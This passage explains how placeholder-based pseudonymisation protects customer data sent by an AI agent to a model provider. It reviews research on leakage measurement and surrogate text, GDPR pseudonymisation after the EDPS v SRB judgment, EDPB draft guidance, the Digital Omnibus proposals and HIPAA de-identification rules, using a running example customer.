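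The choice of strategy explained only about 1% of the variation in scores, because some requests reveal the private fact however they are worded. A request for time off for chemotherapy is hard to disguise if the employer has to approve the treatment dates. Replacement also did worse than no protection in some settings, such as messages to institutions about socially embarrassing matters, although that group of messages was small.

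A false reason may also be a lie. Xiao and colleagues defend the practice as a way for people to control information about themselves, and they exclude medical, legal and safety-critical situations in which the recipient needs the truth. But in one of their examples, a user's partner asks about a named colleague's disciplinary case, and the agent blames someone else, telling the partner that they have mixed up the names. This misleads the partner about another person, which the researchers' own rule forbids.

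The ranking doesn't apply when details are hidden from a model provider. A provider that reads its logs can't ask Maria follow-up questions, so omitting details loses its main disadvantage. In Wen and Li's tests, removing identifying passages protected people about as well as inserting false details. False details, like surrogates, can also mislead the planner.

### When a wrong guess counts as privacy

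Most of these tests count a failed guess as a success for privacy, which can reward the wrong method. Duong, Shin and colleagues (2026) show this in *Residual Attribute Leakage Is an Interface*. They built an editor that replaces words indicating a person's sex with their opposites, such as "he" with "she". A reader who doesn't know about the swap will usually guess the person's sex wrong, but one who does can reverse the guess.

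They measured leakage by how far a text raises a model's confidence in the true answer. If π is the model's confidence without the text and *p* its confidence after reading it, then

leakage = (*p* − π) ÷ (1 − π), or 0 if the result is negative

Suppose the model starts with 50% confidence in the true answer. A text that raises this to 75% has a leakage of 0.5. A text that lowers it to 20% has a leakage of 0, the same as a text that reveals nothing, even though the model now strongly favours the wrong answer.

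On medical exam cases, the swapping editor's text leaked the least of eight versions. It fell to sixth place when the researchers ranked the versions by how well the model's answers separated men from women, even if the model had the labels reversed. When they told the model about the swap, its average confidence in the true answer rose from 25% to 77%.

The choice of measurement mattered less for methods that don't deliberately mislead. Duong and colleagues compared pairs of edited texts and checked whether their conclusions changed when a different model did the guessing. The conclusion changed in 124 of 504 comparisons, but only five reversed which text leaked less. In the other 119, a clear difference appeared or disappeared. In court judgments, whether rewriting words leaked slightly more or slightly less than masking them depended on the model.

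The tests can also measure the wrong person. In the court judgments, the model often answered questions about other people with the sex of the first person named. An order record that mentions both Maria and Mrs Okafor could cause the same mistake, so a low score for Maria might only mean that the model was describing Mrs Okafor.

The result for swapped words matters for surrogates. If an executor always replaced women's names with men's, it would look very private in a test with an attacker that didn't know the rule, but a provider that knew the rule could reverse it. If the executor chose names at random, there would be no such rule to reverse. Providers can read the code of an open-source proxy, so the shop should test its executor against an attacker that knows how the software chooses replacements but doesn't have its keys or mapping table.

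## Pseudonymised data under data protection law

Whether the model provider can identify Maria Keller also affects its legal duties. If the text with her placeholders is still her personal data, the General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR), the EU's main data protection law, covers the provider's copy. If not, the provider could keep the text or train a model on it without having any duties to her under the GDPR.

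If the shop is an Irish company that delivers to Leeds, the GDPR applies to it wherever its customers live. The UK has its own version of the GDPR with much the same definitions, but British courts don't have to follow new judgments from the EU's court.

### The legal definition

Article 4(5) of the GDPR defines pseudonymisation as processing personal data so that nobody can attribute them to a specific person without additional information. The organisation must keep that information separately and protect it so that nobody uses it to link the data to a person.

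The shop's mapping table is additional information in this sense. Keeping it away from the provider is necessary but may not be enough. If the text shows that NAME_1 is a well-known cellist in Leeds, a reader can identify her without the table, so replacing her name and address does not meet the definition.

Under Recital 26, part of the GDPR's introduction, a person is identifiable if the controller or someone else could identify them by means reasonably likely to be used, considering the cost, the time and the available technology. The controller, here the shop, is the organisation that decides why and how to process the data. The shop can look up NAME_1 in its own table, so the whole transcript is personal data for the shop, including the mention of the cello and the remark about Tuesdays.

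Placeholders therefore don't release the shop from the GDPR, but they help it meet several duties:

| Article | Duty | What placeholders contribute | What the shop still has to do |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5 | Process only the data the purpose requires, and keep them secure | The provider doesn't receive an address it has no use for | Drop details such as the Tuesday teaching |
| 25 | Build data protection into the system's design and default settings | The executor replaces values before the planner reads them | Make sure the swap covers tool results too |
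| 32 | Provide security that matches the risk | A thief who copies the provider's logs finds EMAIL_1 | Protect the mapping table |

Articles 25 and 32 both name pseudonymisation as an example of a suitable measure.

### The Board's 2025 draft

The European Data Protection Board (EDPB), which brings together Europe's data protection authorities, adopted draft guidance on these rules in January 2025. Taylor Wessing's *EDPB at a glance* (2025) lists the first steps as replacing or deleting identifiers and storing the additional information separately. Under the draft, the controller should also define a "pseudonymisation domain", the people and systems that must be unable to link the data to anyone. The shop's domain would include the provider, its staff and its contractors.

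The draft took a strict view of which data remain personal. According to the Society for Computers & Law's *EDPB adopts pseudonymisation guidelines and provides guidance on cooperation with competition authorities*, data stay personal if the controller or anyone else can link them back to an individual. On that reading, Maria's transcript would be personal data in the provider's hands for as long as the shop kept the table, even if the provider could not identify her.

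Comments on the EDPB's *Guidelines 01/2025 on Pseudonymisation* (2025) closed on 14 March 2025. Six months later, the EU's highest court took a different view of the recipient's position than the guidelines did, and the Board was still working on the text in February 2026, according to Inside Privacy's *EDPB publishes report on stakeholder event on anonymisation and pseudonymisation* (2026). No final version appears to have been published by December 2026.

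### EDPS v SRB

The court case arose from the collapse of the Spanish bank Banco Popular in June 2017. The Single Resolution Board (SRB), the EU agency for failing banks, had to decide whether former shareholders and creditors should receive compensation. It invited them to comment on its preliminary decision and passed some of the comments to the auditing firm Deloitte, with codes in place of the commenters' names. Only the SRB had the database that linked the codes to people.

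Several authors complained that the SRB had not told them about Deloitte. The European Data Protection Supervisor (EDPS), who oversees the EU's institutions, ruled in their favour. The EU's General Court annulled that decision in 2023, and the EDPS appealed. The case concerned a separate regulation for EU institutions, but Baker Botts' *CJEU Clarifies Requirements and Definition of Pseudonymisation* (2025) points out that this regulation defines personal data and pseudonymisation exactly as the GDPR does.

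On 4 September 2025, the Court of Justice of the European Union (CJEU) held that an opinion necessarily relates to the person who expresses it, according to its press release, *Judgment of the Court in Case C-413/23 P* (2025). The EDPS therefore did not have to examine the content, purpose and effects of each comment to establish that it related to the person who wrote it. By the same reasoning, if Maria complains about the courier's driver, the complaint is information about her as well as the driver.

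The court then held that pseudonymised data are not always personal data for everyone. Depending on the circumstances, pseudonymisation can effectively prevent anyone except the controller from identifying a person. The data are then not personal for those others.

This did not help the SRB, because the duty to inform people arises when the controller collects their data. The SRB knew who they were then, so it had to tell them about Deloitte whether or not Deloitte could identify anyone. The court set aside the General Court's judgment and sent the case back.

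The shop is in the same position as the SRB. It knows who Maria is when she writes her first message, so its privacy notice has to cover the model provider even if the provider will only ever see placeholders. Whether the provider itself holds personal data is a separate question, which depends first on whom it is working for.

### When the provider works for the shop

The EDPB's draft *Guidelines 02/2026 on Anonymisation*, adopted on 7 July 2026, accepts that the same data can be personal for one organisation and anonymous for another. It makes an exception for processors, the GDPR's term for companies that handle data on a controller's behalf. A processor has to adopt the controller's point of view, because otherwise a controller could avoid the law by outsourcing the work.

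In one of the Board's examples, an online retailer sends extracts from its customer records to an agency for analysis. The retailer can identify the customers, so the records are personal data for the agency too. A model provider that processes Maria's messages on the shop's instructions is in the same position as the agency. It needs a data processing contract with the shop, and it must secure its logs, report breaches to the shop and follow the rules on sending data outside the EU.

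Mondaq's *Privacy Corner* (2026) calls this reasoning hard to follow, since an independent recipient could use the same dataset without the GDPR applying, while a processor could not. The objection has some merit, because the provider's technical ability to identify Maria is the same in both roles. But a processor acts for someone who can identify her and returns its answers to them. The shop's executor turns "move NAME_1's delivery" into an action that affects Maria, whether or not the provider knows who she is.

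The provider's perspective matters when it uses the transcripts for its own purposes, such as training a model. Logs that it keeps to detect misuse are harder to classify because their status depends on whether the shop or the provider decides why and how long to keep them.

### What the provider could do with the text

Under the Board's broad definition, an independent recipient identifies Maria if it can distinguish her from other people in a given context and so treat her differently, even without her name. In the Board's example, an advertising company receives pseudonyms derived from visitors' devices and uses them to follow each visitor from site to site. Those pseudonyms are personal data even though the company doesn't have the visitors' names.

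For the same reason, a permanent placeholder such as EMAIL_K7Q2 could be personal data for an independent recipient.

The likelihood of identification only has to be insignificant in practice, not zero. A means of identification may be unlikely to be used if the law forbids it or if it takes disproportionate effort. A contractual ban on re-identification carries less weight than a law because the parties can change or ignore the contract. The Board therefore accepts contracts only as an addition to technical measures. It also cautions against relying on a recipient's lack of motivation to re-identify people.

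The Board expects AI agents to make identification easier, and tests in which models named people from redacted interviews suggest the same. Data that are anonymous today can therefore become personal again, and the Board recommends checking periodically whether they are still anonymous.

To test a dataset, the Board uses three criteria. Applied to an independent recipient of Maria's transcript, they might work out like this:

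| Criterion | What would violate it | Maria's transcript |
|---|---|---|
| No Record Isolation | A combination of details that is unique to one person in the data | Probably only one customer bought a cello, teaches on Tuesdays and lives near the Leeds South depot |
| No Linkage | A match with information about the same person elsewhere | The courier has order 58213 in its own records |
| No Inference | A conclusion about one identifiable person that affects them and depends on these data | Her home may be empty on Tuesdays, if the recipient can work out who she is |

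Data that pass all three tests are anonymous, and data that fail one may still be, but the shop would then have to examine whether the recipient could use the weakness in practice. For example, if only the courier can interpret the order number, the result depends on whether the recipient could get the courier's records.

The Board says controllers should not call data "anonymous" or "de-identified" if people are still identifiable. The shop would therefore take a risk if its privacy notice said "our AI provider receives only anonymous data".

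Public consultation on the draft ended on 30 October 2026. Lewis Silkin's *Digital Rulebook* (2026), published on 10 November, still refers to it as a draft.

### The Digital Omnibus

In November 2025 the European Commission proposed amending the GDPR to state that whether information is personal data depends on who holds it. The proposal is part of the Digital Omnibus, a package of amendments to EU digital laws. National Law Review's *Towards a Contextual Concept of Personal Data Under the GDPR* (2026) reproduces the proposed addition to Article 4(1). Information would not be personal data for an organisation that cannot identify the person by means it is reasonably likely to use. It also would not become personal data for that organisation merely because a possible later recipient could identify the person.

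The second rule conflicts with the Board's draft. Suppose an independent company holds Maria's transcript and cannot identify her, but is likely to pass it to the courier, which can. The transcript would be personal data only for the courier under the Commission's wording, but for both companies in the Board's view.

In February 2026 the EDPB and EDPS (2026) urged lawmakers to reject the proposed new definition of personal data, arguing that it went beyond the court's case law and would significantly narrow the concept. The Council, which represents the member states, then removed the definition from its first compromise. According to Agence Europe's *EU Council effectively kills proposed revision of GDPR*, the Council also deleted a proposed Article 41a, which would have let the Commission help decide when pseudonymised data stop being personal. The EDPB and EDPS also opposed giving the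 Commission that power.

Under the Irish presidency, the idea returned elsewhere in the text. Tar (2026), in *EU governments revise GDPR pseudonymized data rules in new digital package compromise*, reports that a draft of 3 September left the general definition unchanged but stated that pseudonymised data are not personal for an organisation that cannot identify the individual. On 21 October the Council agreed its negotiating position. According to Lewis Silkin, it keeps the definition and adds an Article 25a on when pseudonymised data are personal.

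None of this is law yet. The Council still has to negotiate with the European Parliament, which had not adopted a position by late October, according to The Paypers' *EU Council backs GDPR change on AI data use* (2026). Members of Parliament have proposed more than 1,000 amendments, and Barczentewicz, in *Brussels Tries to Fix the GDPR Without Making It Worse*, expects talks to continue into 2027. In December 2026, the shop therefore has to follow the existing GDPR and the court's judgment.

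### Reward for separation or gap in protection

Supporters of the recipient's point of view argue that the law should give companies a reason to separate data properly. If a recipient faced the same duties with or without placeholders, the shop and its partners would have less reason to build the system. *Context Is Not a Loophole* (2026) warns that controllers who see no benefit in lawful anonymisation may keep processing personal data under heavier and less transparent arrangements.

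Opponents fear that too much data would lose protection. According to The Paypers, the privacy organisation noyb says that user IDs, tracking IDs and IP addresses would regularly fall outside the GDPR, and that companies would largely judge for themselves whether their data counted as personal. The Council has kept the definition's wording, but noyb thinks the new article narrows the definition.

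Mirosław Wróblewski, the head of Poland's data protection authority, points out in Rzeczpospolita's *UE chce zmiany RODO. Po pseudonimizacji nie będzie ochrony* that a recipient for whom the data were no longer personal would not have to secure them under Article 32. If Maria's transcript then leaked from such a company to someone with the courier's delivery list, that person could identify her, even though the GDPR would not have required the company to protect her data.

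The sender also has trouble judging what a recipient can do. Mondaq's *When Is Personal Not Personal?* reports that participants at the Board's stakeholder event asked for guidance on putting data into third-party AI tools. They said businesses often don't know what additional information the next company holds, and that small customers have little power to make large technology vendors tell them.

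Which argument is better for a placeholder system depends on what remains in the text. A request to move DELIVERY_1 to Thursday gives an independent recipient almost no information for identifying the customer, and lighter duties would reward the shop for sending so little. But a recipient with a search tool may be able to identify a customer from a year of conversations about her work, health and purchases, even with every name replaced. The dispute matters less to the shop in ordinary use, because its model provider is usually a processor. According to Lewis Silkin, the Council's Article 25a would also treat processors like the controller they work for.

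### HIPAA: a list or an expert

Under the US health privacy rule, whether data counts as de-identified depends less on the recipient's circumstances if an organisation uses the rule's fixed list of identifiers. The rule, issued under the Health Insurance Portability and Accountability Act (HIPAA), covers most healthcare providers, health insurers and companies that handle patient data for them. It would not cover a cello shop, so suppose instead that Maria lives in Boston and a clinic's agent moves her back treatment from Tuesday 8 December to Thursday 10 December.

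De-identification, as Rijo (2026), in *Explaining de-identification*, puts it, has a legal rather than a technical purpose. Once the clinic has de-identified a transcript, HIPAA's privacy rule no longer restricts its use. Section 164.514 of the regulations offers two ways to do this. The safe harbour method requires the clinic to remove 18 types of identifier:

| Group | Types on the list |
|---|---|
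| Person and place | Names; places smaller than a state |
| Time | All parts of dates except the year, and ages over 89 |
| Contact details | Phone numbers; fax numbers; email addresses |
| Personal numbers | Social security numbers; medical record numbers; health plan numbers; account numbers; certificate and licence numbers |
| Objects | Vehicle identifiers; device identifiers |
| Online | Web addresses; IP addresses |
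| Body | Fingerprints and other biometric data; full-face photographs |
| Anything else | Any other unique number, characteristic or code |

The clinic may keep the first three digits of a postcode if the area they cover has more than 20,000 people. The clinic must also have no actual knowledge that someone could use the remaining information to identify the patient.

The rule on dates is the most awkward for an agent. The planner could not read "8 December" or "Thursday", because both are more specific than the year, so the executor would have to replace them with DATE_1 and DATE_2 and check the calendar itself. The executor would also have to remove "Boston", but could keep "Massachusetts".

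The list is less strict about contextual details. It doesn't include occupation, so the planner could read that Maria teaches the cello, unless that detail was unique to her or the clinic knew it would identify her. The list covers identifiers of the patient and of her relatives, employers and household members, but it doesn't explicitly cover those of a neighbour such as Mrs Okafor.

The clinic must remove every listed identifier, so a transcript with a single missed email address does not qualify. Many long transcripts would fail even with a good detector.

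HIPAA also restricts how the clinic makes its placeholders. The clinic may use a code to re-identify records later, but it must not derive that code from information about the patient or disclose how to reverse it. A counter such as EMAIL_1 or a random token meets the first condition, but a keyed hash does not, because the software calculates it from the patient's email address or name.

The other route is expert determination, in which someone with suitable statistical and scientific knowledge must conclude that the risk of an expected recipient identifying a patient is very small, and document the methods and results. The expert considers the text together with other information reasonably available to that recipient. This test is closer to Recital 26 and could allow the planner to read a treatment date if the rest of the transcript revealed little.

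An expert can't review each of the agent's requests while a patient waits, so the clinic would need approval for a defined process, including the detector, the details it lets through and the recipients. The expert would have to test that process on real transcripts, and review it again if the clinic added a search tool or changed to a provider with more information about the clinic's patients.

If the transcript meets HIPAA's conditions, it is de-identified even for the clinic, which still holds the mapping table. But under the GDPR, the table makes the same transcript personal data for the clinic and, in the Board's view, for any provider working on its behalf.

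A clinic that cannot meet either standard can sign a business associate agreement with the model provider, which makes the provider directly responsible for protecting patient data. The planner may then read the real appointment dates. Placeholders for the name and medical record number would still limit the damage from a leak, but the transcript would remain protected health information.
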